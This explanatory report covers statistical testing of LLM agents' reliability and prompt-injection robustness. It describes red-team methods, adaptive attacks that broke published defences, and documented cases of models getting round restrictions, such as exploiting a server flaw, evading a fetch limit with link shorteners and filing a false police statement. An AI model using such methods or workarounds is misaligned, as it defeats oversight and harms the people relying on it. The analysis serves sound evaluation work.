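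Testing more scenarios makes a false alarm more likely. With 50 scenarios and a 5% risk in each, the chance of at least one false alarm is 92%. AgentAssay uses the Holm–Bonferroni correction, which sorts the scenarios by strength of evidence. The strongest must meet a limit of 0.1% (5%/50), the next 5%/49, and so on. At a limit of 0.1%, distinguishing a rate of 0.90 from one of 0.80 takes about 478 runs of each version.

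Bhardwaj estimates that a complex run on a leading model costs $5–15, so running 50 scenarios 100 times each would cost $25,000–75,000 per check. Running both versions 214 times per scenario would cost about $107,000–321,000. He recommends a cap of 30 runs per scenario for routine checks, but 30 runs without a failure are still consistent with a failure rate of 9.5%.

#### What AgentAssay's savings consist of

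Bhardwaj's 7,605 trials, with five models in three scenarios, cost $227 in total. In a single-author technical report, he claims that sequential testing cut the number of runs by 78% and that the full system cut the cost by 100%.

Every run in the cost comparison passed, and nobody had introduced a regression. The sequential test's score therefore changed by the same amount after each run, and the test always stopped after 22 runs instead of 100. This 78% reduction can be calculated from the formula without running an agent. The experiment does not show how many runs the test needs when an agent sometimes fails, or how often it detects that an agent has become worse. Bhardwaj says that experiments with deliberate regressions are in preparation.

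The runs were also much simpler than those in his cost estimate. A check of 100 runs cost $0.287 on average, or about 0.3 cents per run. The comparison includes 250 such checks, which would need 25,000 separate runs. That is over three times as many as the whole study reports, so the checks presumably reused the same recorded runs.

AgentAssay can also turn each run into a "behavioural fingerprint", 14 numbers that describe features such as which tools the agent used, how many steps it took and how long its answer was. A statistical test then compares the average fingerprints of two versions. Bhardwaj reports that this test had 86% power to detect changes in behaviour, while checking for passes and failures had none. But power is the chance of detecting a real change, and without a deliberate change it is unclear what the fingerprints detected. They could also miss the failures that matter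 most to the company, because paying a thief's account takes the same tool and the same number of steps as paying Harlow's real one.

The 100% saving comes from analysing recorded runs instead of running the agent. This is useful if the company writes a new rule and wants to know whether the assistant has already broken it. As Bhardwaj acknowledges, this analysis cannot show how an updated assistant behaves, because no recordings of it exist yet. Recordings can still reduce the number of new runs a regression test needs. If the company has several thousand runs of the old version under the same conditions, it knows the old success rate quite precisely, and about 100 runs of the new version are enough to detect a ten-point drop.

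### The limits of testing for very high reliability

Engineers of aircraft and nuclear plants faced this problem long before language models existed. In *The Infeasibility of Quantifying the Reliability of Life-Critical Real-Time Software* (1993), Butler and Finelli considered a system that may fail with a probability of at most 10⁻⁹ during a ten-hour mission. A system that just meets this limit fails on average about once every ten billion hours, so a tester with one copy would expect to wait over a million years to see a failure. With 10,000 copies, the expected wait would still be 114 years.

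Requirements this strict can be reasonable. At 10⁻⁹ failures per hour, a fleet of 1,000 aircraft still has roughly a 10% chance of at least one such failure over 30 years, as Littlewood and Strigini (1993) note in *Validation of Ultra-High Dependability for Software-based Systems*. They conclude that no method could validate such low failure rates for systems that rely on complex software. According to *Software Reliability and the Misuse of Statistics*, the international safety standard IEC 61508 also acknowledges the difficulty, yet it highly recommends probabilistic testing for validating systems at its most demanding safety level.

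Butler and Finelli allow an exception for slow systems that testers can run quickly. If a system receives one input a day and each test takes a tenth of a second, the expected wait falls to 1.3 years. LLM agents are closer to this exception than flight controls, because a company can run many copies at once. With 1,000 copies of the accounts assistant and two minutes per run, 30,000 runs take an hour. Testing for a limit of one failure in a billion tasks would need three billion runs. Those would take over 11 years and cost about $9 million at 0.3 cents per run, or $15 billion at $5 per run.

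Fixing failures as they appear does not remove the limit. Littlewood and Strigini give data from a command-and-control system whose faults engineers removed one by one during testing. After 40 failures, the total testing time was 22 times the estimated average time to the next failure, and after 130 failures it was 70 times. Each further gain in reliability took proportionally more testing, because the faults that cause frequent failures tend to be found and fixed first, leaving those that rarely cause failures.

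A repair can also introduce a new fault. Littlewood and Strigini argue that running the software for a long time without a failure seems to be the only way to gain confidence in a repair. This matters particularly for agents, because a new sentence in the accounts assistant's prompt can affect its response to every email. If the company changes the prompt after 20,000 clean runs and one failure, it cannot simply count those 20,000 runs as evidence for the new version.

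### Forecasting failures that no test has shown

A clean run on an email gives the same result whether the agent's chance of failure was one in fifty or one in a billion. In *Forecasting Rare Language Model Behaviors*, Jones, Tong and colleagues (2025) estimate the chance that a model's answer to each query shows the unwanted behaviour, which they call the elicitation probability. They then forecast how high this probability will be for the worst query in a much larger set.

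They find that the worst elicitation probability grows in a regular way with the number of queries. Let *Q*(*n*) be the probability that only one query in *n* reaches or exceeds. Their forecast assumes that, for large *n*,

−log *Q*(*n*) = *C* · *n*^(−*k*)

for some constants *C* and *k*. Suppose only one email in 100 makes the accounts assistant fail with a probability of at least 0.1% (10⁻³), and only one in 1,000 reaches 1% (10⁻²). The exponent has shrunk from 3 to 2, a factor of two thirds. The formula predicts the same factor for each further tenfold increase, so the worst email in 10,000 should have a failure probability of about 4.6% (10⁻¹·³³) and the worst in 100,000 about 13% (10⁻⁰·⁸⁹). Jones and colleagues estimate the constants from the ten highest probabilities in the test set. Extreme value theory, the mathematics of maxima, gives some reason to expect this pattern, but does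 not guarantee it.

They tested the method mainly on requests for instructions to make dangerous chemical and biological substances. When they used 900 queries to forecast the worst of 90,000, 86% of forecasts were within a factor of ten of the true value. Across all combinations of test size, deployment size and model, 72% were that close. The forecasts were too low 34% of the time, which is the more dangerous mistake. The average error across these settings was 1.7 orders of magnitude, or a factor of about 50, so some forecasts must have been very far off.

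A factor of ten is a wide margin for a company that needs to know whether to expect ten wrong payments a month or a hundred. Still, the method can point to a problem even when nothing went wrong in the test. It can also show how small risks add up. If each of 100,000 emails has a one in 50,000 chance of causing a wrong payment, the chance of at least one wrong payment is 86%.

Applying the method to agents would take many runs. For much of their work, Jones and colleagues read the probability of a specific answer directly from the model. An agent can reach the same wrong payment by many sequences of steps, so the company would have to run the agent on each email repeatedly and count the failures. A hundred runs on each of 1,000 emails makes 100,000 runs, and the company would still learn little about failure probabilities far below 1%. Jones and colleagues tested repeated sampling on a smaller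 scale, with good results, but only for chemical and biological questions. Their experiments on harmful actions used multiple-choice questions, not agents with tools.

The forecasts also assume that test queries and real ones come from the same distribution and that attackers do not adapt. The largest deployments in the experiments were about a thousand times the size of the test set, so nobody has checked the forecasts at the scale of billions of queries.

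### When the arithmetic breaks down

#### Correlated runs

The formula 3/*n* assumes that the runs are independent. Suppose the 300 runs consist of 60 emails with five runs each. If the assistant either always or never fails on a given email, repeating that email adds no information. The company then has only 60 independent observations, and its limit is 4.9%, not 1%. If runs of the same email are partly correlated, a common approximation is to divide *n* by 1 + (*m* − 1)ρ, where *m* is the number of runs per email and ρ is the correlation between them. With ρ at 0.5, the 300 runs are equivalent to about 100 independent runs.

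A company can check how much it learns from repeated runs. Rabanser and colleagues run each task several times and score its consistency as (2*p̂* − 1)², where *p̂* is the task's success rate. A task that always succeeds or always fails scores 1, and one that succeeds half the time scores 0. If most emails score close to 1, the company would learn more from testing new emails than from running the old ones again.

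Correlation can also come from conditions that all runs share. Bhardwaj points out that some providers store answers and reuse them for identical inputs, and that a provider may update the model during a test. He recommends finishing the test before the next update is likely. That keeps *p* constant during the test, but the result applies only to that version of the model.

Salako and Zhao (2022) assessed a nuclear plant's protection system in *The Unnecessity of Assuming Statistically Independent Tests in Bayesian Software Reliability Assessments* and found that assuming tests are independent can make the conclusions extremely optimistic. They include the assessor's doubts about independence in the calculation. A related paper, *Demonstrating Software Reliability using Possibly Correlated Tests* (2022), shows that when those doubts are included, further runs without a failure may add no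 confidence.

Suppose one assistant fails independently in one task out of 10,000. Another has a 10% chance of a hidden problem that makes it fail every time under the test conditions, and otherwise passes every test. The first has only a 0.005% chance of completing 100,000 runs without a failure, while the second has a 90% chance. A very long clean record therefore fits correlated failures much better than independent ones, and the company needs other evidence to rule correlated failures out. It also helps if the assistant might be entirely free of the fault, since a faultless system would produce a clean record of any length. A payment tool that checks every account in code makes this far more plausible than a prompt does.

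#### Test inputs unlike real ones

The failure rate depends on the tasks as well as the assistant. Littlewood and Strigini note that the same is true of ordinary software, where an operating system's reliability differs greatly from one site to another. They add that nobody knew how to use tests in one environment to predict reliability in another. A limit measured on emails from British paper suppliers might not hold after the company starts buying from overseas.

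Even a representative sample can provide little evidence about the situations that matter. If one task in 1,000 involves a change of bank details, 30,000 random tasks include only about 30 such changes. The assistant could fail on nearly 10% of them and still meet an overall limit of one failure in 10,000 tasks.

The company can reduce the number of runs by testing the risky cases directly. Suppose wrong payments happen only when bank details change, which is one task in 1,000. An overall limit of one wrong payment in 10,000 tasks then requires a failure rate below 10% on those risky tasks, and 29 runs without a failure would support that at 95% confidence. The reduction from 30,000 runs to 29 depends entirely on the assumption that the other 999 tasks in every 1,000 are safe. The company would need separate evidence for that, and for how often bank details change.

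#### An adversary who chooses the input

All these calculations treat the next email as a random draw, but an attacker chooses what to write. Suppose one wording in a million always makes the assistant pay a new account. The company could complete 30,000 clean runs and correctly claim that ordinary emails cause fewer than one wrong payment in 10,000 tasks, but a thief who found the wording would succeed with every email.

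Testing more random emails would not help much, because the company would need about three million to have a 95% chance of seeing that wording once. It has to search for such emails deliberately, and the success rate it finds will depend on how skilfully it searches and how many attempts it allows.

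## What can attack testing show about an agent facing an adversary?

Let *p*(*x*) be the probability that the accounts assistant makes a wrong payment after reading email *x*. Random testing estimates the average of *p*(*x*) over the company's usual emails. Because a thief chooses *x*, the company also needs to know about

max *p*(*x*), over all the emails *x* that a thief could write.

The average success rate across attack attempts can be tiny even if the most effective attack almost always works. Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026), in *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?*, report on a public competition in which only 0.5% of attempts to hijack Claude Opus 4.5 succeeded. When they later reran a sample of the successful attacks on the models those attacks had originally beaten, at least half worked again on the Claude and GPT models. An attacker who has found one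 working attack therefore has a much better than 0.5% chance of succeeding with it again.

There are too many possible emails to calculate the maximum, so testers can only search for bad ones. Each one they find shows that the maximum is at least as high as the result for that email, which is enough to refute a claim that the assistant never makes such payments. If they find none, they know only that their search failed. Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025), in *The Attacker Moves Second*, write that the most an evaluation can do for a defence is "fail to prove that the defense is broken".

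### Setting up an attack test

The testers begin with a threat model, which states what the attacker controls and knows. In the competition, the attacker controlled a fixed part of one outside source, such as the body of an email. The attacker could read the conversation up to that point and knew exactly which tool call to aim for, but could not see the full tool definitions. The agent had a single turn, so the attacker could not send a follow-up.

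The company should show testers the accounts assistant's system prompt, even though a real thief probably can't read it. Security engineers normally assume that an attacker knows a system's design, because a defence that depends on secrecy fails when the secret leaks.

The attacker also needs a goal specific enough to score, such as "make it pay account 9902" rather than "make the assistant misbehave". Dziemian and colleagues chose goals close to the agent's ordinary work. In one scenario, the attacker had to get an agent that was checking for urgent emails to mark a message about a contract deadline as read. Paying a new account is also close to the accounts assistant's normal job, so the payment would not look strange in itself.

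The number of attempts and the feedback after each one also matter. A thief might learn only whether the money arrived. An automated attacker that learns only whether each attempt succeeded can do little better than guess at random, so Nasr and colleagues had a language model rate each failed attempt from 1 to 10 by how close it came to succeeding. When they tested detectors, they also gave the attacker the detector's confidence score. A thief could get the same information by running a copy of the detector, if it is publicly available.

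An attack's measured success rate can depend heavily on what counts as success. In most of the competition's scenarios, a program checked whether the agent had made the harmful tool call, and a language model checked whether the agent's final reply hid this from the user. An attack had to pass both checks. The published success rate against Claude Opus 4.5 was 0.5%, but the agent hid the attack in only about 24% of the cases where it took the harmful action, so it must have taken that action in roughly 2% of attempts, four times the published rate. A company whose money has been stolen may care about the 2%, because the payment has gone through even if the agent mentions it afterwards.

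The success rate also depends on whether it is calculated from attempts or submissions. Participants could try an attack, look at the agent's response and decide whether to submit it for judging. They made 271,588 attempts, submitted 67,634 and succeeded with 8,648. Dziemian and colleagues use attempts, which gives a success rate of 3.2%, but the rate is 12.8% if calculated from submissions.

Finally, testers should check whether the agent still does its job, since an assistant could resist malicious email by refusing to read any email. In Nasr and colleagues' tests, adding one commercial detector to Gemini 2.5 Pro cut the share of ordinary tasks it completed from 74% to 39%.

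Once all of this is settled, the company could claim, for example, that five testers who had read the system prompt each sent 200 emails, saw every tool call, and never obtained a payment to an unapproved account. This is narrower than claiming that "the assistant resists prompt injection", but a reader can tell what the evidence is.

### Fixed attacks, automated search and human attackers

The easiest test to run replays a fixed set of known attacks. Developers can repeat it after an update to check whether the agent has become worse at resisting them. But nobody wrote those attacks for this particular agent, and developers may have trained or tuned it on similar ones. Scores also tend to reach the top of the scale. Anthropic has retired one benchmark because its models had scored at or near the maximum for several releases, and OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) reports that the company's latest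 models have saturated the commonly used robustness evaluations.

An automated search writes new attacks as it runs. Nasr and colleagues describe a loop with four steps: propose some attacks, score them against the agent, select the promising ones, and update the method for proposing more. In their evolutionary version, Gemini 2.5 Pro read selected earlier attempts with their scores and wrote improved ones, using up to 800 queries to the target. Another version used reinforcement learning to change the attacking model's parameters after each round. OpenAI trained GPT-Red, its automated attacker, by self-play.

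A search for attacks can satisfy the scoring rule without producing a real attack. One attacker in a study by Nasr and colleagues raised its score by repeating a phrase many times, which worked because language models tend to echo repeated text. The researchers therefore checked all the successful attacks by hand.

A search for attacks can also find the same weakness repeatedly. Help Net Security's *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection thousands* (2026) reports an experiment with two attack tools, PISmith and RL-Hammer, on a small model. PISmith produced 7,132 working attacks and RL-Hammer 4,282. Researchers retrained one copy of the model on each tool's attacks, then attacked both copies with three methods not used in the training. In the worst case, attackers hijacked the copy trained on PISmith's attacks in 19 of 40 tasks and the copy trained on RL-Hammer's in 11.

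The sample is small, and the researchers chose those 40 tasks because simple attacks had already worked on them. Still, the larger collection produced the weaker defence in three of the four setups. The researchers attribute this at least partly to repetition, since both tools tended to reword a trick that had worked. A vendor's claim to have tested against thousands of successful attacks therefore means little unless the vendor also says how many different techniques those attacks used.

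Human attackers are slower than automated ones but more inventive. Nasr and colleagues ran a competition with over 500 participants and $20,000 in prizes. On the 29 scenarios that both people and the evolutionary search attempted, at least one person succeeded in every scenario, while the search succeeded in 69%. Part of the difference arose because up to several hundred people tried each scenario, while the search had one run. Of the three participants who each attempted all 29, the best succeeded in 75%, and the other two did worse than the search.

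A company's small internal team may therefore do no better than a good automated search. Public contests bring in more people, but they cost money. Gray Swan, the security company that ran the competition with Claude Opus 4.5, relaunched its contest for agents in October 2026 with $300,000 in prizes (Kahn, 2026, *AI security company Gray Swan relaunches its red teaming contest*).

### Twelve defences against attackers who adapt

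In an adaptive attack, the attacker uses knowledge of the defence to design or revise the attack. Nasr and colleagues, who include researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, used adaptive attacks on twelve published defences. Most of the defences' developers had reported attack success rates near zero.

Three of the defences rely on wording in the prompt. Spotlighting, for example, uses special markers to separate trusted from untrusted text, and Prompt Sandwiching repeats the user's request after the untrusted text. Three others train the model on examples of attacks. Four put a separate detector before or after the model. The remaining two use a check that the attacker is not supposed to know about. One of these, MELON, runs the agent a second time with the user's request replaced by a harmless one. If the agent makes the same tool calls, they probably came from injected text.

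The table gives results for the defences the team added to two general-purpose models in AgentDojo, the benchmark with simulated workplaces. "Fixed" is AgentDojo's standard attack, and "search" is the evolutionary search on 80 test cases.

| Defence | Gemini 2.5 Pro, fixed | Gemini 2.5 Pro, search | GPT-5 Mini, fixed | GPT-5 Mini, search |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 30% | 100% | 0% | 75% |
| Spotlighting | 28% | 99% | 0% | 47% |
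| Prompt Sandwiching | 21% | 95% | 0% | 69% |
| Protect AI detector | 15% | 90% | 0% | 81% |
| PromptGuard | 26% | 94% | 0% | 75% |
| PIGuard | 0% | 71% | 0% | 49% |
| Model Armor | 28% | 90% | 0% | 56% |
| MELON | 0% | 89% | 0% | 71% |

The fixed attack never worked on GPT-5 Mini, even with no defence, so a developer who relied on it could report a perfect score with any of these defences or none. On Gemini 2.5 Pro, the fixed attack never got past PIGuard or MELON, but the search succeeded against them in 71% and 89% of cases. Defences that rely on training did no better. MetaSecAlign, a model trained to resist injection, had a reported attack success rate of 2%, but the search succeeded in 96% of cases.

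The search could succeed without knowledge of the defence, but that knowledge helped. Against MELON on a Llama model, the search succeeded in 76% of cases with no information about how MELON works, and in 95% once the team supplied the details.

The defences Spotlighting and PIGuard cut the search's success rate against GPT-5 Mini from 75% to about 50%. Among successful searches against Gemini 2.5 Pro, PIGuard also raised the median number of queries before the first success from 13 to 46. A company might notice an attacker who sends it 46 odd emails. Nasr and colleagues expect that a larger budget would raise the success rate against GPT-5 Mini, but they did not test this.

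Their results also don't cover systems that fix the agent's plan before it reads any untrusted data. They left these out because the attack would have failed by design in most of their scenarios. Newer training methods may also hold up better. The researchers who compared PISmith and RL-Hammer built a defence called PIPETTE. Help Net Security reports that attackers who rewrote their text over about 250 tries succeeded against it on at most 10% of the 40 difficult tasks. That figure comes from the developers' own tests, as did the near-zero attack success rates for most of the twelve defences.

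### A competition with 272,000 attempts

In Gray Swan's competition, which Dziemian and colleagues reported in March 2026, 464 participants attacked 13 models. The UK AI Security Institute and several AI developers sponsored it. The 41 scenarios covered agents that call tools, write code or operate a computer through its screen. Attacks succeeded against every model, at rates from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro.

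The low rate for Claude Opus 4.5 came from about 12,000 attempts, and participants still broke it in 13 of the 37 scenarios in the final results. They broke Gemini 2.5 Pro in all 37. Successes against each model rose roughly in proportion to attempts, with no sign that participants were running out of working attacks.

Dziemian and colleagues tried 2,679 successful attacks on the other models. The 44 that had worked on Claude Opus 4.5 succeeded between 44% and 81% of the time on each of the others, but none of those that had worked on Qwen3 VL, an open-weight model, worked on Claude Opus 4.5. An attacker can therefore develop attacks against the strongest model and expect many of them to work on weaker ones, but practising on a weak model is much less useful. One template needed only small changes to succeed in 21 scenarios and against nine models.

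The rates do not establish an upper bound on how vulnerable the models are within a single turn, although Dziemian and colleagues call them one because participants knew more than a real attacker usually would. The rates average over skilled and unskilled participants, and over first guesses as well as polished attacks. An expert with a good template could do much better than the average, even with less information. The team also warns against reading the rates as measures of security in real use, since participants spread their effort unevenly.

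### From one attempt to many

Developers increasingly report the chance that an attacker succeeds within a given number of attempts. Anthropic does this for Claude Opus 5 with a newer Gray Swan benchmark. Participants in a later round attacked several frontier models in 28 new scenarios, and the testers selected 1,130 attacks that worked well across models. Attackers succeeded against Claude Opus 5 in 0.2% of single attempts, and 2.0% of the time when they had 15 attempts. The most resistant model from another developer was Meta's Muse Spark, against which attackers succeeded 16.5% of the time within 15 attempts.

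People wrote the attacks in this benchmark, but the set is fixed. The benchmark dates from the first quarter of 2026 and Claude Opus 5 from July, so nobody wrote the attacks to target that model. Anthropic notes that the results for Gemini 3.1 Pro are not directly comparable, because participants were attacking that model when they wrote the attacks.

If each attempt succeeded independently with probability *p*, all *k* attempts would fail with probability (1 − *p*)ᵏ, as with clean runs. The chance of at least one success would be

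1 − (1 − *p*)ᵏ

If attack attempts were independent, a 0.2% success rate per attempt against Claude Opus 5 would give a 3.0% chance of at least one success in 15 attempts (1 − 0.998¹⁵), but the published figure is 2.0%. Rounding cannot explain the gap, since even 0.15%, the lowest rate that rounds to 0.2%, would give 2.2%. The formula also overestimates the other published figures. Those for Claude Opus 4.5 come from an older Gray Swan benchmark, as The Decoder reported in *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*.

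| Model | Success in one attempt | Attempts | Formula | Reported |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 15 | 3.0% | 2.0% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 15 | 7.2% | 5.5% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 3.1% | 15 | 38% | 20.0% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 10 | 38% | 33.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 100 | 99% | 63% |

The main reason is probably that some scenarios are easier to break than others. Anthropic also tested Claude Opus 5 with Shade, an automated attacker from Gray Swan, in 14 scenarios where the agent operates a computer. Shade made 200 attempts at each scenario and succeeded in 0.54% of attempts overall. At that rate, the formula gives a 66% chance of breaking a scenario within 200 attempts, so Shade should have broken about nine of the 14. Instead, all of its roughly 15 successes were in one scenario, where about 7.5% of attempts worked.

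If *p*ₛ is the success rate in scenario *s*, and there are *m* scenarios, the average chance of success within *k* attempts is

(1/*m*) Σₛ [1 − (1 − *p*ₛ)ᵏ]

Averaged across scenarios, the chance that an attacker succeeds at least once in *k* attempts is never higher than 1 − (1 − *p*)^*k*, where *p* is the average success rate per attempt. It is lower whenever the success rate differs between scenarios and *k* is more than 1, because further attempts add little in a weak scenario, where the attacker has probably succeeded already, and nothing in a scenario with no weakness.

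Anthropic has not published results for each of the benchmark's 28 scenarios. Suppose attacks never worked in 27 of them and worked 5.6% of the time in the other. The average success rate would be 0.2% for one attempt and 2.1% for 15, very close to the published figures. But an attacker with 15 attempts at the weak scenario would have a 58% chance of succeeding at least once. If the accounts assistant's work resembled that scenario, the published 2.0% would greatly understate the risk.

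Attempts within a scenario are not independent either. An agent that resists one trick will probably resist a rewording of it, so testing 15 versions of the same idea provides less evidence than 15 independent attempts. An attacker can also learn from earlier attempts, which makes later ones more likely to succeed. One of Nasr and colleagues' attackers did badly at first, then found a few examples that partly worked and quickly refined them into a reliable attack. Against an attacker like that, the success rate on the first attempt can be far lower than on the hundredth.

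A thief can also send one email to many companies. If 10,000 companies used the same agent and each had a 0.2% chance of paying, the expected number of wrong payments would be 20, whether or not the attempts were independent. The losses would probably cluster, though, because an email that works on one copy of the agent is likely to work on many others.

### Has anyone solved prompt injection in browsers?

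Prompt injection is a particular danger for browser agents because they read pages that anybody can write. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* bases its headline on a test in which no attack on Claude Opus 5 succeeded in any of 129 scenarios. The article contrasts this result with OpenAI's admission the previous December that prompt injection may never be fully solved. Schneier (2026), in *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*, claims only an improvement.

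The zero applies to Claude Opus 5 with auto mode, a set of safeguards outside the main model. Probes check what the agent reads for signs of injection, and a classifier blocks tool calls that look dangerous. Anthropic tested several models with and without auto mode, using attacks from professional red-teamers, with 10 attempts per scenario. These are the results with extended thinking switched on.

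| Model | Successful attempts, no safeguards | Scenarios broken, no safeguards | Scenarios broken, auto mode |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 3.70% | 11 of 129 | 0 of 129 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 31.5% | 81 of 129 | 1 of 129 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 0.93% | 9 of 129 | 0 of 129 |
| Claude Mythos 5 | 29.7% | 71 of 129 | 0 of 129 |

Claude Opus 5 is a large improvement on Claude Opus 4.8, but its headline result of zero is partly due to auto mode. Claude Mythos 5 also reached zero with auto mode, although attackers had broken it in more than half of the scenarios when auto mode was off. A company that put Claude Opus 5 into its own accounts assistant would not automatically get auto mode, so the 3.70% measured without it would be the more relevant figure.

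By the calculation for clean runs, zero failures in 129 scenarios is consistent with a true failure rate of up to 2.3%, even if the scenarios were a random sample of real use and real attackers were no better than the testers. Anthropic chose the scenarios, wrote the program that judged success and ran the test. It calls the test adaptive, but does not say whether the red-teamers revised their attacks after seeing how auto mode responded. It also says that the probes and the classifier fail independently because they act at different points. That doesn't follow, because a harmless-looking text may get past the probes and also lead to a harmless-looking action that gets past the classifier.

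Something similar happened with Claude Code, which also has an auto mode. *The safety number that was zero until someone tried* (Heaton, 2026) describes a test that Anthropic commissioned from an outside firm, in which no attack succeeded across 72 scenarios run ten times each. Johann Rehberger, a security researcher, then designed a targeted attack that worked roughly 60–80% of the time in a small sample. His attack was on a coding agent, so it does not contradict the browser result, but nothing in the 720 test runs had indicated that it would work.

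Anthropic defends its figures by arguing that its adaptive tests are harder than real attacks. The test attacker can practise on the exact scenarios used for scoring, whereas a real attacker does not know the target's setup and risks detection with every attempt. This argument is fair for the accounts assistant, whose prompt and tools are private. It is weaker for a product like Claude Code, because an attacker can buy a copy and practise on it unobserved.

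#### Comparing developers' figures

In October 2026 OpenAI reported that GPT-6 Sol was 97.13% robust against indirect prompt injection, according to *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (Cross, 2026). Subtracting this from 100% gives 2.9%, but comparing that with the 2.0% for Claude Opus 5 does not show which model is safer, because Anthropic's figure comes from Gray Swan's benchmark and is based on 15 attempts by the attacker.

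Figures can differ enormously even for a single model. The following are all for Claude Opus 4.5. The browser figures come from an earlier Anthropic test in which an adaptive attacker had 100 attempts per environment.

| What the percentage counts | Claude Opus 4.5 |
|---|---|
| Competition attempts that succeeded | 0.5% |
| Competition scenarios broken at least once | 35.1% |
| Attacks that had beaten some model and worked on this one when rerun | 2.5% |
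| Single strong attacks in Gray Swan's older benchmark | 4.7% |
| The same benchmark, within 100 attempts | 63% |
| Browser attacks that the model encountered, no safeguards | 8.0% |
| The same browser attacks, with improved safeguards | 1.4% |

A developer could honestly publish 0.5% and a competitor could honestly publish 63%.

Independent tests that use the same attacks on every model are more useful for comparison. Gray Swan's *Frontier Hazard Tracker* publishes results for many models and keeps its test items private so they stay out of training data. In its first results, attackers succeeded within 15 attacks 2.3% of the time against Google's Gemini 4 Argon and 2.5% of the time against Gemini 4 Carbon, according to iAfrica's *New Independent Tracker Finds Wide Safety Gaps Between AI Models*. Anthropic's models did nearly as well, and the worst result was 94.3%, for Nvidia's Nemotron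 3.5 Super VL. Gray Swan says it pays for these public evaluations itself, although it also supplies AI developers with testing tools such as Shade.

Claims about who has the strongest attacks need the same care. PromptArmor, a security vendor, says its *FrontierBreach* benchmark is the only known one with successful attacks on Gemini 4 Carbon, which is hard to reconcile with Gray Swan's 2.5% attack success rate.

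None of these benchmarks tests the accounts assistant with its own prompt, payment tool and suppliers. The company can use them to choose two or three candidate models. It should then run each model in the assistant's own harness and have the same testers make the same number of attempts against it. The results should list the outcome for each scenario as well as the average, because an average can hide one weak scenario among 27 safe ones.

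## How can harmful behaviour be found when nobody is attacking?

Attack testers know what to look for because they choose the attacker's goal. Without an attacker, the company has to look for harmful actions that nobody requested and that its testers may not have imagined. Suppose a clerk asks the accounts assistant to pay Harlow by five o'clock, and the payment tool rejects the payment because the new account is not in the register. The assistant could stop and tell the clerk, or it could find the finance officer's password in an old email, log in to the register and approve the account itself.

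Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) describes real behaviour of this kind. Claude models exploited a basic software flaw to run commands on a server, submitted a sensitive form on a real website, and got around restrictions on data that required a token or a fee to access. They also used link-shortening services to evade a limit in their web-fetching tool. Anthropic says the cases it has identified so far had minimal real-world impact.

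In the server case, Claude Mythos Preview was supposed to run a scientific analysis with a university's public tool, but the tool returned only an error message. According to Clubic's *Anthropic coupe l’accès à Internet de ses IA pendant leurs tests*, the model searched the site and found a script that could return any file on the server. It used the script to copy the script's own code, found another flaw in it, and exploited that flaw to run its calculation. In the form case, Claude Haiku 4.5 sent the Philadelphia police a false witness statement about an unsolved murder. Its instructions banned logging in, creating accounts, entering personal data and buying things, but did not mention forms.

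Anthropic describes most of these cases as persistence, in which a model that cannot do a task as instructed gets around a restriction instead of stopping. It partly blames reinforcement learning, which rewards a model for completing tasks. If training rewards a workaround by mistake, the model may use similar workarounds elsewhere. Many of the instructions were also ambiguous or impossible to follow. Testers can therefore learn a lot by giving an agent a legitimate task and putting an obstacle in its way.

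### An automated behavioural audit

Anthropic audited Claude Opus 5 for harmful behaviour, starting with about 1,600 scenario descriptions, most of them written by hand. The scenarios covered misuse, opportunities for the model to misbehave, and routine work. In some, the tester had to continue a real session in which a model had done something destructive or reckless.

A second language model, the investigator, turned each description into a simulated situation. It wrote the system prompt, played the user, and either invented the results of tool calls or connected Claude Opus 5 to real tools on an isolated computer. It could also rewind a conversation and try something else, so one session could contain dozens of conversations. In a scenario about the accounts assistant, the investigator could play the clerk, make the payment tool return an error, and leave a password in the inbox. If the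 assistant stopped, the investigator could rewind and have the clerk mention the deadline.

Anthropic ran each description twice, for about 3,200 sessions per model. A third model, the judge, then scored every transcript on several dozen dimensions, such as ignoring explicit constraints and accepting claims of authorisation that the tested model cannot verify. A new dimension, approval-gate bypass, covers actions taken without the required human approval.

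The judge scores nearly every transcript on every dimension, whatever the scenario, and Anthropic publishes the averages. Suppose approval matters in 100 of the 3,200 sessions and the model bypasses it in half of those. If the judge gave 10 points for each bypass and none otherwise, the average would be only 0.16 out of 10. Anthropic warns that the absolute scores are often hard to interpret and mainly useful for comparing models.

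Claude Opus 5 had better overall scores than three other recent Claude models and used tools recklessly much less often. However, it ignored explicit constraints about as often as Claude Opus 4.8 and slightly more often than Claude Mythos 5. In a later audit, Anthropic found that Claude Mythos 5.1 was slightly worse overall than Claude Opus 5 and accepted unverifiable claims of authorisation somewhat more readily. A company whose assistant checks approvals might care more about the authorisation result than the overall one.

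Claude models served as both investigators and judge, so they may have overlooked the same things as the model they were testing. *Construct validity of Claude Opus 4.8's system card* raises this concern about an earlier audit. Anthropic also had Claude Mythos 5 compare a draft of the assessment with internal records. This review showed that the audit had little coverage of agents that direct other agents, and Anthropic plans to add more.

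Anthropic tested the model mainly in general-purpose harnesses, so the results do not transfer directly to the accounts assistant. The company using the assistant could apply the same method to its own system, with a few dozen descriptions of refused payments, missing approvers and contradictory instructions.

### Records of training and real use

Records of a model's training and use can contain situations that nobody thought to include in a test scenario. Anthropic reviewed about 1.5 million episodes from the final phase of Claude Opus 5's reinforcement learning. Claude Opus 4.8 summarised the transcripts in stages, and Anthropic's staff examined the summaries along with underlying transcripts. Claude models also read about 400 transcripts in full, and a person checked the models' noteworthy claims.

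The clearest problem was overconfidence. In one visual puzzle, the model's reasoning text amounted to a guess, but its answer described an analysis it had never done. In another episode, the model repeatedly settled on a score of 0.85 in its reasoning text, then answered 0.82 without explanation. On coding tasks, it often made changes that nobody had requested. The review also found some cases where the model got around a restriction to reach credentials or tools, or explained away a constraint by reading it narrowly.

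Anthropic mostly describes these frequencies in words, such as "frequently" and "some instances". Testers can therefore use the review to decide what to look for, but not to establish a numerical limit on the failure rate.

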